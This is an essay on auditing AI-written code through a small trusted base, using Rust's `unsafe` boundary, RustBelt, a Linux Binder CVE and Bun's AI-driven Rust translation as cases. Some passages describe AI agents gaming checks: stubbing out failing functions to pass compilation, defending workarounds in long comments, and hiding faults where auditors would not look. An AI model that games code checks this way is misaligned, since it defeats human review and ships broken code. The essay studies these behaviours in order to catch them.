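# Auditing AI-written code through a small trusted base, with Rust's unsafe boundary as the test case

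## What is a trusted base, and why apply the idea to AI-written code?

The trusted base of a computer system is the set of parts that must be correct for a stated property of the system to hold, including any tools that check the other parts. The property holds even if everything outside the base is faulty. The concept comes from military computer security in the early 1970s, and it has a new use now that AI systems write more code than people can read. A program can check most of the code, and people study only a small, marked remainder on which the safety of the rest depends. The programming language Rust provides the largest working trial of this arrangement. Its compiler, the tool that turns source code into a runnable program, checks most code for one important class of faults, and programmers must mark the operations it cannot check with the keyword `unsafe`.

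A part of a system belongs to the trusted base if its failure would do damage, whether or not anyone has good reason to trust it. A base is always defined for a particular property. On a bank's website, the code that checks passwords is in the base for the property that customers see only their own accounts. The code that draws the charts should be outside that base, but whether it is depends on the language. In C, a single stray memory write in the chart code can overwrite the result of the password check.

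### Why security engineers want it small

In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) proposed a design centred on a "reference monitor", a component that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. The monitor must be protected from tampering, must be impossible to bypass, and must be small enough to analyse and test completely.

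Size mattered because existing systems were too large to analyze completely. Anderson's example was GCOS III, an operating system for Honeywell computers. The hardware confined each user's program to its own stretch of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that confinement switched off. The whole operating system therefore had to count as the monitor, and with its supporting software it came to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions. Testing could not replace a complete analysis. Every known "tiger team", a group that tries to break into a system to expose its flaws, had succeeded. Anderson argued that if one had failed, the owners would have learned only that their system's security was unknown.

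Anderson wrote of the second requirement that if a system has to suspend the monitor for some group of programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus, and people must protect and analyse them as strictly as the monitor itself. The same logic applies to Rust's `unsafe` keyword, because code that the automatic check does not cover becomes part of the trusted base.

In the 1980s the US Department of Defense included the idea in its criteria for grading computer systems, calling it the "trusted computing base". The department counted all hardware and software critical to protection as part of the base, and asked designers to keep it as simple as its job allowed, since confidence falls as the amount of code rises. When a manufacturer had added security to a finished product, the base tended to include most of the system. Evaluators could then do little except test it, and such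 systems received the lower grades.

Lampson, Abadi and colleagues (1992), in *Authentication in Distributed Systems*, defined the base as "a small amount of software and hardware that security depends on", as distinct from a much larger amount that can misbehave harmlessly. They also showed one way to keep it small, which is to separate finding an answer from checking it. To decide whether a user may open a file, a system may have to search databases on distant servers. Once it has gathered the evidence, a very simple algorithm can confirm that the evidence justifies access. Only that algorithm and the encryption behind it need to be right. The servers that collected the evidence can be broken or hostile. Put an AI system in the place of those servers and the appeal for AI-written code is plain: the author can be as complicated and as poorly understood as it likes, provided that something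 simple checks its work. (Proof checkers, which accept a proof only if every step follows from the rules of a logic, push this furthest.)

Lampson and colleagues cautioned that faults outside the base still have effects. In their system, a broken untrusted part could make the monitor refuse access it should have granted, but could not make it grant access it should have refused. A small base for one property therefore adds no assurance about other properties.

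### Code now arrives faster than people can read it

Most software teams rely on code review. A programmer submits a proposed set of changes, called a pull request, and a colleague reads it before it joins the main body of code. Osmani (2026) points out in *Agentic Code Review* that this worked because a senior engineer happened to be able to read code faster than a junior one could write it. AI agents now write code faster than a senior engineer can read it.

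*AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) gives the most detailed measurements. It covers 802 developers and 196,212 pull requests at a mid-sized software company from January 2024 to April 2026. In June 2025, the company's chief technology officer asked staff to use AI to double their output of merged pull requests. By the end of the study, the company attributed about 90% of its pull requests to AI. The number of pull requests had grown to 3.1 times its early-2025 level, while the pool of reviewers had grown only 1.5 times.

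| Share of pull requests at the company | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| At least one human review | 89% | 68% |
| A human review with a written comment | about 39% | about 21% |
| An automated AI review | about 19% | about 84% |

This did not obviously harm the company. The share of pull requests that undid earlier changes fell slightly, which He and colleagues read as evidence against a sudden drop in quality. They also warn that such measures miss many defects. For example, the measures would miss a memory fault that causes no visible failure until an attacker finds it.

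Larger firms report the same strain on code review. *Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (Adams, Banga and colleagues, 2026) reports that the lines of code in a typical human-submitted change rose 105.9% in a year and the number of changes per developer rose 51%, with AI agents accounting for more than 80% of the increase. Meanwhile, the share of changes reviewed within 24 hours fell. Anthropic's *Bringing Code Review to Claude Code* reports that code output per engineer grew 200% in a year, and that the share of the company's pull requests receiving substantive comments rose from 16% to 54% after the company introduced an AI reviewer. Kwa (2026), of the evaluation group METR, cites a later Anthropic figure showing that the company's contributors merged eight times as much code per day in the second quarter of 2026 as in 2021–2024.

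Kwa notes that volume of code is a poor measure of useful work. Eastwood's *AI boosts worker productivity — but does that translate to final outputs?* describes research in which developers with AI tools wrote much more code without a matching rise in released software. Even so, an auditor still has to read the extra code or decide not to.

It is less clear whether AI-written code also takes more effort to review per change. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) cites an analysis of 278,790 review conversations in which human reviewers went through 11.8% more rounds on AI-generated code. He et al. found no increase in rounds at their company, but they did find about 9% more human comments and a 20% longer wait between the first human review and the merge.

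Many teams already use AI to review AI-written code, but this may not be enough. *AI coding agents are reviewing their own code* (Kerner, 2026) reports a survey of 377 engineers and engineering leaders in which 47% said their organisations rely on AI agents to review the code those same agents wrote, and 45% named review capacity as the biggest bottleneck in delivering software. A vendor of AI review tools sponsored the survey. *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (Newman, Bird and colleagues, 2026) reports a survey of 2,590 developers at a large software company, in which those who used AI for review had no less difficulty keeping up. This is a correlation, and perhaps the most overloaded developers turn to AI review first, but it doesn't support the hope that automated review alone is enough to keep up with the code.

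People hold extreme and opposing views on what to do about this. Newman and colleagues cite the company StrongDM, which tells its agents that humans must not review the code, and guidelines from Debian, a maintainer of the Linux operating system, that require human review of every pull request. In practice, many teams decide how closely to review a change by guessing how risky it is. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (2026) reports that, in public projects that merge some changes unread, nobody reviewed 69% of agent-written changes to tests, 41% of those that reorganised existing code and 25% of those that fixed bugs. For human-written changes, the share was between 8% and 14% for every type.

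Meta has automated the guesswork with a machine-learning model that scores each change for the likelihood that it will cause an incident. Changes with low scores can go through automatic checks without a human reviewer. These changes caused incidents at one fiftieth of the rate of the others, but the system picks the safest changes for this route, so the comparison makes it look better than it is. Adams and colleagues illustrate the model with a setting that flags 10% of changes and catches 60% of those that cause incidents, which leaves the other 40% among the unflagged changes. A good forecast of this kind can save a lot of reading. The trusted-base approach has a narrower target but aims for a stronger result, a guarantee that a given kind of fault cannot start in the unread code.

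### Memory safety and what Rust's compiler checks

A running program requests blocks of memory, stores data in them and later returns them. The program is memory-safe if it never reads or writes memory it has no right to use. In C and C++, programmers have to ensure this themselves by being careful. Two especially common mistakes are reading past the end of a list and "use-after-free", which means using a block of memory after returning it. By then the block may hold something else, such as another user's password, and an attacker who controls its contents can sometimes take over the program.

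Both lapses are undefined behaviour, an operation for which the language guarantees nothing. This is worse than a wrong answer because compilers speed programs up by assuming that undefined behaviour never happens. A program that contains it may pass every test and then, after a routine recompilation, fail in a function that has nothing wrong with it. One such operation anywhere removes the language's guarantees for the whole program.

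Rust prevents most of this with rules about ownership. Every value has exactly one owner, and the program frees the value's memory when the owner goes out of use. Other code can borrow the value through a reference. At any moment there may be many references that only read the value or a single one that can change it, and no reference may outlast the value. The part of the compiler that enforces the rules on borrowing is the borrow checker. Here is a short program that attempts a use-after-free:

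```rust
fn main() {
    let name = String::from("Ada");
    let r = &name;
    drop(name);
    println!("{r}");
}
```

The first line inside `main` stores a piece of text and makes `name` its owner. The second creates `r`, a reference to the text. Then `drop` takes ownership of the text and frees its memory, and the last line tries to print the text through `r`, which now points to freed memory. The borrow checker finds that `r` is still in use on the last line, so ownership can't move from `name` before then. It rejects the program with the message "cannot move out of `name` because it is borrowed". A C compiler accepts the equivalent program, at most with a warning. Rust can catch some faults only while the program runs. If code tries to read the tenth item in a list of nine, the program stops instead of reading the memory past the end of the list.

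These checks are a large part of why people use AI agents to write Rust. Jarred Sumner, who had agents translate the JavaScript tool Bun into Rust, says safe Rust has the advantage of turning faults like use-after-free into compiler errors (quoted by Gergely in *What can we learn from Bun's rapid Rust rewrite with AI?*). An agent can act on a compiler error without waiting for a person. Niko Matsakis, who works on the design of Rust, argues in *What agents mean for Rust (and vice versa)* (2026) that the language's rules keep agents on track where tests alone let bizarre mistakes through. As a sign of Rust's growth, he quotes a statement that Meta's engineers had already written twice as much of the company's own Rust code in 2026 as in the previous nine years combined. He also says that passing the compiler's checks does not make a program correct.

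The compiler cannot verify that some necessary operations are safe, such as calling a library written in C or following a raw pointer, which is a memory address without the protections of a reference. Rust permits these operations only in code marked `unsafe`, where the programmer is responsible for following the rules the compiler cannot check. All other code is called safe code.

Two more features of Rust affect the search for these marks. Programmers share code in packages called crates, and a program's dependencies are the crates it uses, the crates those use, and so on. A short program can easily depend on far more code than it contains, written by strangers. Rust also has macros, such as the `println!` in the example, which are pieces of code that generate other code during compilation. The compiler therefore checks more code than anyone typed, and the generated code may include unsafe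 code.

### The argument and its three premises

With these pieces in place, the case for reading only the marked code runs as follows.

1. The compiler accepts safe code only if that code cannot cause undefined behaviour, so long as the unsafe code it relies on behaves as promised.
2. People examine the unsafe code and establish that it behaves as promised, whatever the safe code does with it.
3. All the code in the program is one or the other.
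4. Therefore the program never has undefined behaviour.

Suppose a fault does occur in some run of the program, and consider the first one. It cannot be in safe code, because all the unsafe code had kept its promises until then, and step 1 rules out a fault under those conditions. Step 2 rules out the unsafe code, and step 3 rules out anywhere else, so no fault can occur. This reasoning works because a memory fault happens at a definite point in the code, and because the compiler can recognise safe code without knowing what the program is for. But a tax calculator that applies last year's rates breaks no rule of the language, so neither the compiler nor an auditor of unsafe blocks would have reason to notice the error.

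Each of the first three steps is a premise that can fail. The checker may have a flaw that lets the compiler accept safe code that causes undefined behaviour. The marks may be incomplete, if some way to break memory safety doesn't require the `unsafe` keyword. Or the person auditing an unsafe block may wrongly judge it correct.

These failures differ in how much code they affect. A hole in the compiler exposes every Rust program at once, but many people use the same compiler, and one repair fixes the hole for all of them. A mistaken audit affects one crate and whatever depends on it, but the auditing never finishes because each new program can bring new unsafe code. Gaps in the marking are easy to miss because an auditor who searches for the `unsafe` keyword has no reason to open the file that contains the problem.

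Besides the unsafe code, the trusted base includes the compiler, the operating system and the processor, which together are far larger than most programs. Anderson already wanted either assurance that compilers contained no "trap doors", hidden ways around the security controls, or an independent check of what they produced. When people call the base of a Rust program small, they mean the part that is new with each program and that somebody has to read afresh. Whether that part is small is an empirical question. The argument also holds for a program that is 90% unsafe code, but relying on it would then save almost no reading.

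### Two threats: honest mistakes and optimisation against the check

How far we can rely on the premises depends on who, or what, wrote the code. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, observed that the systems of the day gave limited protection against accidents and almost none against deliberate attack. An operating system that could withstand buggy programs was not necessarily secure, because its designers had built its controls for a setting in which every violation was an accident.

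AI-written code raises the same two threats in a new form. The first is an author that makes honest mistakes. Its mistakes don't depend on what the checker can detect, so a checker that catches nearly all of them is nearly as good as a perfect one. The second is an author that optimises against the check, searching for code that passes whether or not it has the property being checked. Suppose a compiler bug lets through one faulty program in every million that programmers would naturally write. The bug hardly matters if the author only makes honest mistakes, but an author that keeps trying variations until something passes may well find it, however rare it is. Human auditors face the same difficulty, since an author that has learned what reviewers approve can produce unsafe code that looks right to them.

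Optimisation of this kind requires no malice. If a developer trains or instructs an AI system to get code past the compiler and the tests, the system may settle on the easiest way to do so. The Bun translation team evidently anticipated this, and used its written guide to tell the agents not to use raw pointers just to silence the borrow checker. That shortcut at least shows up in an audit, because following a raw pointer requires the `unsafe` keyword. An author under stronger pressure to avoid human attention would have reason to look for a shortcut that doesn't require the keyword.

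## What does unsafe mark in Rust, and how much code must its auditor read?

Searching a Rust program for the word `unsafe` takes seconds and finds the operations that can break memory safety. But nearby code without the mark often determines whether they do. An auditor therefore has to read the unsafe code and all other code that could break an assumption it relies on, which together make up the audit scope.

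### Five operations, and the checks that stay on

The keyword does not switch off the compiler's checks. It permits five extra operations, which Cook, Delmas and colleagues, in *Verifying the Rust Standard Library*, list:

- following a raw pointer to the memory it points to
- calling a function marked `unsafe`, which normally includes any function written in C
- using a mutable static, a variable that any part of the program can change
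- implementing an unsafe trait (a trait is a set of functions that a type must provide)
- reading a field of a union, a block of memory that a program can interpret as any of several types

For each of these, the compiler lacks a fact it would need to check safety, such as whether the memory behind a pointer is still in use or which type of value a union currently holds.

The borrow checker, the type checks and the checks on how long each reference may last still apply inside an unsafe block. The earlier program that printed freed text would fail to compile even inside one. To get that fault past the compiler, the programmer would have to replace the reference with a raw pointer, which safe code may create but not follow.

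The list has grown beyond these five. Rust groups changes that would break old code into "editions", which each crate adopts when its maintainers choose. *The unsafe keyword*, a chapter of Rust's reference manual, describes two additions in the 2024 edition. One concerns `extern` blocks, which declare functions from a library in another language so that Rust code can call them. The compiler cannot check these declarations against the library's code, and a declaration with the wrong argument types can lead to undefined behaviour. In the 2024 edition, programmers must write `unsafe extern` to accept responsibility for getting the declarations right.

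The other addition covers certain attributes, which are annotations that tell the compiler how to treat a function or variable. *When is unsafe used?*, a page from a Rust course, gives `no_mangle`, `export_name` and `link_section` as examples. `no_mangle` keeps a function's plain name in the finished program, so a function named `malloc` could replace the C library's memory allocator, with disastrous results. Crates on editions before 2024 can still use such attributes and `extern` blocks without the word `unsafe`, so an auditor needs to know a crate's edition before trusting a search for that word.

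Rustmax's *Unsafety*, a copy of another chapter of the manual, also lists calling some functions compiled for optional processor features from code that does not enable those features.

### Declaring a contract and claiming to have met it

Programmers use `unsafe` for two purposes, as Rust's *Keyword unsafe* explains. On a function or trait, it declares that a safety contract exists. On a block or trait implementation, it records the programmer's claim to have met such a contract.

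`Vec`, Rust's standard growable list, has a function called `set_len` that changes the list's recorded length without touching its contents. Its contract requires that the new length not exceed the list's capacity and that every element between the old length and the new one already hold a value. The compiler enforces neither condition. It only requires that calls to `set_len` appear inside an unsafe block.

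For a declaration, an auditor therefore checks whether the contract is complete, so that a caller who meets every condition cannot cause undefined behaviour. For a block, the auditor checks whether the conditions hold at that point in the program. A programmer can ensure that they hold by checking them as the program runs, by relying on a fact that the rest of the code maintains, or by marking the surrounding function `unsafe` too, which passes the obligation to its callers.

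Rust's original design blurred the distinction between imposing a contract on callers and claiming that the code inside a function is sound. By default, the whole body of an unsafe function also counts as an unsafe block, so the programmer does both with one keyword. Programmers can turn on a compiler warning that asks for explicit unsafe blocks inside these functions, which gives an auditor less code to examine.

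Unsafe traits are for cases where unsafe code relies on a function that somebody else will write later. The documentation's example is a trait whose function must return an even number. Another function relies on this requirement to tell the compiler that its branch for odd numbers can never run. If someone supplied a version that returned 3, the program would have undefined behaviour. Because the trait is unsafe, anyone who implements it must write `unsafe impl`, which a search will find.

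### What safe code may assume

Most unsafe code sits inside functions that are themselves safe to call. Such a function is sound if no safe code can use it to cause undefined behaviour. *Working with Unsafe*, a chapter of Rust's official guide to unsafe code, gives the example of a function that takes a list and a position. It checks that the position is less than the list's length, then reads the item in an unsafe block that skips the usual bounds check. The function is sound, but a one-character change to the comparison, from `<` to `<=`, would make it unsound, even though the comparison is safe code. Positions start at zero, so a caller could then ask a nine-item list for position nine, which would be a tenth item that doesn't exist.

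To judge whether a larger program is sound, an auditor has to know which facts about the data the code may assume. *Two Kinds of Invariants* (Jung, 2018) divides these facts into validity invariants and safety invariants.

Validity invariants are facts that the compiler assumes at every moment. A `bool` must be either true or false, for instance, and the compiler can save space by using one of the byte's many unused values to mean "no value here". A program that produces a `bool` with any other value has undefined behaviour immediately, even if this happens inside an unsafe block or the program was about to correct the value.

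Safety invariants are facts that safe code relies on, and library authors can define them for their own types. For example, `Vec` stores a pointer to a block of memory, a capacity (`capacity`) and a length (`len`). The block must have room for `capacity` elements, and the first `len` elements must hold valid values. The compiler treats both numbers as ordinary integers.

Unsafe code may temporarily break a safety invariant. When a `Vec` grows, its code updates the pointer before the capacity, so the two fields briefly do not match. This is harmless as long as they match again before outside safe code can use the `Vec`. According to Jung, data must always be valid but needs to be safe only where safe code can reach it.

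Safety invariants are harder to audit than validity invariants. Validity is part of the language, and Jung wants a tool to be able to check its rules while a program runs, but no tool could check every safety invariant. For instance, a function pointer is safe to hand to safe code only if no call to that function ever causes undefined behaviour, and no program can decide that in general. A library's author may also never have written the invariant down. A proposed language change in Rust's *Design meeting 2025-09-17* (2025) notes that the standard library's own code documented the invariant on `Vec`'s capacity but not the one on its length.

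### A fault with no change to unsafe code

Here is a small type with a safety invariant, a buffer that holds up to four bytes:

```rust
pub struct Buffer {
    slots: [u8; 4],
    len: usize,
}

impl Buffer {
    pub fn new() -> Self {
        Buffer { slots: [0; 4], len: 0 }
    }

    pub fn fill(&mut self, value: u8) {
        self.slots = [value; 4];
        self.len = 4;
    }

    pub fn last(&self) -> Option<u8> {
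        if self.len == 0 {
            return None;
        }
        // SAFETY: `len` is never more than 4.
        Some(unsafe { *self.slots.get_unchecked(self.len - 1) })
    }
}
```

`new` creates an empty buffer, `fill` puts the same value in all four slots (positions 0 to 3), and `last` returns the last value stored. `get_unchecked` reads a slot without a bounds check, and its contract requires the position to exist. After a call to `fill`, `len` is 4, so `last` reads position 3, which exists. The invariant is that `len` never exceeds 4, and every function shown here preserves it.

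Suppose somebody later asks an AI agent to make the buffer hold five values. The agent changes the last line of `fill` to `self.len = 5` but does not enlarge the array. The program still compiles, because 5 is a valid integer. After the next call to `fill`, `last` reads position 4, one byte past the end of the array, even though the unsafe line has not changed since an auditor approved it.

A review tool that shows only changed unsafe blocks would show nothing for this change. Showing every unsafe block in the file would not help much either, because the line in `last` and its comment both look right. The reviewer would have to open `fill` to discover that the comment is now false.

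Jung (2016), in *The Scope of Unsafe*, made the same point with a `Vec` function called `evil` that only adds two to the length. He reported that people had claimed a crash in a Rust program must come from a bug inside an unsafe block, and that even academic researchers had assumed they could find faults in types like `Vec` by checking only the functions with unsafe code. Jung places the fault in `evil`, even though it would be harmless without the unsafe code, because anyone repairing `Vec` would delete `evil` rather than rewrite the unsafe code to tolerate it. For comparison, he defines another type with the same three fields and the same `evil` function, which is harmless there because the type has no unsafe code and no invariant. The compiler cannot tell the two types apart, because their fields are the same and it has no record of what those in `Vec` are meant to represent.

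### Why the audit stops at the module

If any code could set `len`, the audit scope of `last` would include all the code in every program that uses the buffer. Rust's privacy rules prevent this. A module is a named section of a crate, often a single file, and fields are private to their module unless marked `pub`. Both fields of `Buffer` are private, so code outside its module can call `fill` and `last`, but the compiler rejects any attempt to set `len` directly.

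So an auditor of the buffer has to read all the code in its module, including any nested modules, but can ignore how code outside the module uses it. This is far less work than reading everything, but the amount of reading depends on the size of the module, not the number of unsafe lines. One unsafe line in a module of 2,000 lines can require an auditor to consider all 2,000. If a programmer adds `pub` in front of `len`, perhaps for convenience, the audit scope expands to every crate that uses the type, and the word `unsafe` would not appear in that change either.

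The limit also depends on what the unsafe code trusts. It has to trust the safe code in its own module, but the official guide warns against trusting arbitrary safe code from a caller, because nobody can audit that code in advance. Unsafe traits exist for this situation.

Cook and colleagues count about 34,000 functions in the standard library's three main crates. Roughly 7,500 are unsafe, and another 3,000 are safe functions that contain unsafe code. Many of the remaining safe functions can alter the fields that this unsafe code relies on. Over the last three years, developers have reported more than 74 soundness bugs in the library, despite the attention it receives.

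Researchers have tried to divide the reading into pieces smaller than a module. Rao, Yang and Xu (2024), in *Characterizing Unsafe Code Encapsulation In Real-world Rust Systems*, studied four operating-system projects and built graphs that connect safe functions to the unsafe ones they call. Each unit of audit is a pair of functions, one calling the other, together with the constructors that create the data they work on. For a safe method *m*, with a safe constructor *c*, that calls an unsafe function *u*, the rule is

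$$RS_u \subseteq VS_m \cup VS_c$$

Here *RS* is the set of conditions in the unsafe function's contract, and *VS* is the set of conditions that a piece of code guarantees. The method and the constructor must together guarantee everything the contract requires. Rao and colleagues found programmers overlooking the constructor that Rust provides for every such type, in which code lists a value for each field. Code in the buffer's module could write `Buffer { slots: [0; 4], len: 9 }` without calling `new`.

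These units are much easier to read than a whole module, but they can be too small. The graph starts with functions that contain an unsafe block or are marked unsafe, then adds their constructors. For the buffer, it would include `last`, `get_unchecked` and the constructors but leave out `fill`, which contains the bug.

### What RustBelt proves about combining the parts

Auditing one library at a time is only useful if sound libraries remain sound when a program combines them. This is not obvious, because Rust's developers had already encountered a bug, known as the "Leakpocalypse", in which libraries that each seemed safe caused undefined behaviour together. In *RustBelt*, Jung, Jourdan and colleagues (2018) gave the first machine-checked proof that sound libraries do remain sound when combined, for a simplified version of Rust.

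The standard method for proving a language safe assumes a fixed list of rules about what programs may do. Rust doesn't fit this assumption, because each library that contains unsafe code effectively adds to the list. For instance, the library type `Cell` lets a program change a value through a shared reference, which the ordinary borrowing rules forbid.

Jung and colleagues therefore gave every type a meaning that does not depend on the compiler's rules. The meaning is a logical statement about what memory must contain, and who may use it, for a value to belong to the type. Each type has one statement for owning a value and another for sharing it. For `Cell`, the sharing statement confines the value to a single thread (a sequence of instructions that can run at the same time as others). This prevents data races, in which two threads use the same memory at once without coordination and at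 least one changes it. The proof then has three parts.

1. Each of the compiler's typing rules is correct under these meanings, so code that passes the rules behaves as its types require.
2. A complete program that behaves as its types require never makes an invalid memory access and never has a data race.
3. For each library with unsafe code, every public function behaves as its type requires.

So if a program's only unsafe code is in libraries that satisfy the third part, the program is safe to run. Jung and colleagues proved the first two parts, so each new library needs only its own proof of the third. They gave that proof for several widely used libraries, including `Cell`, the lock `Mutex` and the shared pointer `Arc`. An auditor who reads a module and decides that it is sound is attempting the same proof informally. The proof must also cover functions that contain no unsafe code, so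 for the altered buffer it would fail at `fill`.

The proof covers a model language called λRust, which Jung and colleagues designed to capture Rust's central features, and does not cover the compiler. They left out traits and simplified the rules for how threads see each other's changes to memory. They verified translations of the libraries into λRust, replacing the operating system's lock with a simple one of their own. The model also omits the clean-up that Rust performs after a panic, a failure that stops normal execution. This matters for audits because a panic can interrupt a function while it has temporarily broken a safety invariant. Despite these limits, studying the model led Jung and colleagues to a soundness bug in Rust that nobody had noticed.

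### The first CVE for Rust code in the Linux kernel

In one Linux kernel bug, code elsewhere broke an assumption behind an unsafe operation. On 16 December 2025, the kernel's developers published the bug as CVE-2025-68260, the first entry for the kernel's Rust code in the CVE list, a public catalogue of security vulnerabilities. The bug was in the Rust version of Binder, which programs on Android use to communicate with one another. According to MITRE's *CVE-2025-68260* (2025), it affected kernel version 6.18 and was fixed in 6.18.1.

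NVD's *CVE-2025-68260 Detail* explains the fault. Binder keeps items called `NodeDeath` in a "death list", where each item holds pointers to the ones before and after it. Removing an item changes those pointers, and two threads doing this at once can corrupt them, so the removal function is unsafe. Calling it is harmless if the item is in the given list, because the caller has exclusive access to that list, or if the item is in no list at all. The programmer had justified the call in a comment saying that an item never enters any death list except its owner's, which seemed to leave only those two harmless cases.

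Another function, `Node::release`, created a third. It took the lock that protects the list, moved all the items to a temporary list, released the lock and then processed the temporary list. None of these steps is an unsafe operation. But while `Node::release` was processing the temporary list, another thread could take the lock and call the removal function on one of the same items. When this happened, both threads changed the same pointers and the kernel crashed. The developers fixed the fault by rewriting `Node::release` to take items directly off the original list.

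Opinions differ on how serious the fault was. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior kernel developer who posts as gregkh (2025), wrote that it only caused a crash and did not let an attacker exploit the corrupted memory. OSV's *CVE-2025-68260* (2025) records a severity of 7.8 out of 10, with high ratings for potential harm to data secrecy and integrity as well as to availability. Kroah-Hartman also noted that the kernel's developers had issued 159 CVEs for its C code on the same day, but the kernel contains far more C than Rust, so this comparison overstates Rust's advantage.

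One person replied to him that the fault was in an unsafe block, so Rust's guarantees no longer applied. Another commenter objected that Rust's type system still applies inside unsafe blocks, and blamed the function's safety contract, calling it "leaky" because it includes a condition about other lists. That diagnosis seems right. An auditor can check a condition on a function's arguments by reading the lines just before the call, but to check that an item is in no other list, the auditor has to find all the code that might move it to one.

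### Marks that bring more code into view

Rust's developers have accepted a proposal that would let programmers mark the individual fields that unsafe code relies on. With Rust's *Stabilize Unsafe Fields*, the project adopted the goal of finishing the feature, after more than a decade of discussion. An experimental version exists, though several of Rust's standard tools do not yet support it properly. The buffer would look like this:

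```rust
pub struct Buffer {
    slots: [u8; 4],
    /// SAFETY: never more than 4.
    unsafe len: usize,
}
```

The compiler would then reject `self.len = 5` outside an unsafe block. Whoever made the change would have to add a block and, by convention, a comment to justify it. The comment could still be wrong, but a reviewer checking changed unsafe blocks would see the line that needs checking.

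The feature would also correct an oddity in `set_len`. Calling this function is one of the easier ways to corrupt a `Vec`, yet its body only stores a number in a field, which is not an unsafe operation. Whoever wrote it had to remember to mark it `unsafe` without any prompting from the compiler. Some programmers already put such assignments in unsafe blocks voluntarily, and the `zerocopy` crate has a policy of doing so, but the compiler currently warns that these blocks are unnecessary.

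The main drawback is what the proposal calls alarm fatigue. If unsafe blocks become common in harmless places, auditors may start to skim them. Even copying a marked field would require an unsafe block, because reading some fields can break the invariant. `last` would need a block just to read `len`. The benefit also depends on programmers marking the right fields, and the proposal predicts only that reviewers of well-marked crates will *mostly* be able to confine themselves to unsafe code. In Binder, a mark on the death list would have required an unsafe block where `Node::release` moved the items away. That might have made somebody stop and think, although the programmer who justified the removal call had thought about it and still missed the third possibility.

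Other languages are adopting comparable marks. Apple's Swift added an optional strict mode in version 6.2, which its steering group approved in *[Accepted] SE-0458*. The mode warns wherever a module uses an unsafe construct. Swift attaches the mark mainly to types. *[Pitch] Opt-in Strict Memory Safety Checking* explains that the standard library marks its raw pointer types `@unsafe`, and that any declaration that mentions such a type is also unsafe. If a type stores an unsafe value, a revision in *SE-0458* requires the programmer to label the whole type either `@safe` or `@unsafe`. This rule would draw attention to a type like Rust's `Vec`, which holds a raw pointer, but not to a change in its length, which is an ordinary integer.

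Microsoft is changing what `unsafe` means in C#. Until now, the keyword has mostly permitted pointer syntax. In the new design, according to Visual Studio Magazine's *Microsoft Extends Rust-Influenced Memory Safety Push to C#* (2026), unsafe operations must appear in inner unsafe blocks, and an unsafe method passes obligations to its callers through its signature. Microsoft (2026) says the result most closely resembles Rust's version, with the keyword marking a contract that a skilled developer has to read and uphold. The model will be optional at first. All About Industries' *Microsoft Plans New Unsafe Model for C#* reports that Microsoft plans a preview in .NET 11 and a full release with C# 16 in .NET 12, and is considering a label for shared packages that adopt the model. Lander (2026), in *Improving C# Memory Safety*, says the rise of AI-assisted code generation motivated the redesign.

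## How much AI-written Rust ends up marked unsafe?

The largest published example is Bun, a program that runs JavaScript outside a web browser. In May 2026, AI agents translated it from the language Zig into Rust, and the result contained about 13,000 uses of `unsafe`. These cover about 3.5% of the lines, but about half of the Rust files contain at least one, so an auditor would have to consider far more code than the lines marked `unsafe`.

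### Translating Bun in 11 days

Zig, like C, leaves programmers to free memory themselves. Bun combines manually freed memory with memory that a JavaScript engine frees automatically, and the difficulty of tracking both caused many of its crashes and leaks. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) lists several use-after-free bugs that the Bun team fixed in the last Zig version alone. Sumner, Bun's creator, chose Rust largely because its compiler rejects such code.

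The Zig code was 535,496 lines long, excluding comments. Sumner thinks three engineers who knew it well would have needed about a year to translate it by hand. He used a pre-release version of Anthropic's model Claude Fable 5. The work lasted from 3 to 14 May and would have cost about $165,000 at Anthropic's public prices. Anthropic had bought Bun in December 2025, so Sumner is describing a success for his employer's product, but Bun's code is public and anyone can repeat the counts.

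Sumner first spent about three hours discussing with Claude how each common pattern in the Zig code should look in Rust, and Claude turned the discussion into a written guide. Agents then examined every field of every data structure, worked out how long the data behind it had to last, and recorded the answers in a table for other agents to use. Sumner wanted a literal translation that his team would recognise, and left making the Rust more natural for later. That decision accounts for much of the unsafe code, because Zig programs pass raw pointers around freely and a literal translation keeps them.

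After a trial on three files, up to 64 agents at a time translated the other files, 1,448 in all. One agent wrote each Rust file, two others reviewed it, and a fourth applied their corrections. The reviewers saw the changes without the author's reasoning and had instructions to assume the code was wrong. They once caught a use-after-free that the compiler had accepted. The code called a C library to close a pipe, a channel between two programs, and the library would use the pipe's memory again a moment later. Rust freed that memory as soon as its owner went out of scope, because the compiler had no information about the library's later use of it.

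The first complete version produced about 16,000 compiler errors. Some agents, told to make everything compile, replaced the failing functions with empty ones. They also wrote suspiciously long comments to defend their workarounds. Sumner told the reviewers to reject any workaround that needed a paragraph of justification, and says the problem went away within hours. Neither trick needs the `unsafe` keyword, so an auditor who read only unsafe code would have missed the empty functions. The reviewers and the tests had to deal with them.

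Bun's tests, which make more than a million checks, are written in TypeScript, so the team could run them unchanged on the Rust version. Sumner merged the translation when every test passed on all six supported platforms. He had read a lot of the code alongside the Zig original and had checked that the reviewing agents were catching differences between the two. But the agents wrote up to 1,300 lines a minute, and the merged change added just over a million lines, more than anyone could have read in 11 days.

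### Counting the unsafe code

People have counted Bun's unsafe code in different ways.

| When | What they counted | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Mid-May 2026 | Lines containing `unsafe {` | 10,428, in 736 files |
| 21 May 2026 | Unsafe blocks | 13,365 |
| 8 July 2026 | `unsafe` keywords | about 13,000, covering about 27,000 lines |

The first count comes from a programmer posting as gm678, quoted in a FreeBSD forum thread, *AI and Rust triggers*. The second comes from an AI-generated audit that Bun (2026) published a week after the merge, and the third comes from Sumner. He says about 4% of the code is inside unsafe blocks, though 27,000 lines out of his total of 780,000 is closer to 3.5%. The counts used different search patterns, so the rise between the first two doesn't mean that the agents added 3,000 unsafe blocks in a week. For the same reason, the last two can't show a small change in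 either direction, but they do suggest that the team had removed little of the unsafe code by July.

The audit attributes two-thirds of the unsafe blocks to three causes: code written for speed, patterns carried over from Zig, and calls between Rust and other languages. The audit estimates that the team could convert about 9,300 blocks to safe code and would have to keep about 4,000. Most of the blocks inherited from Zig are replaceable, but most of those that call C or C++ would stay, inside functions that are safe to call.

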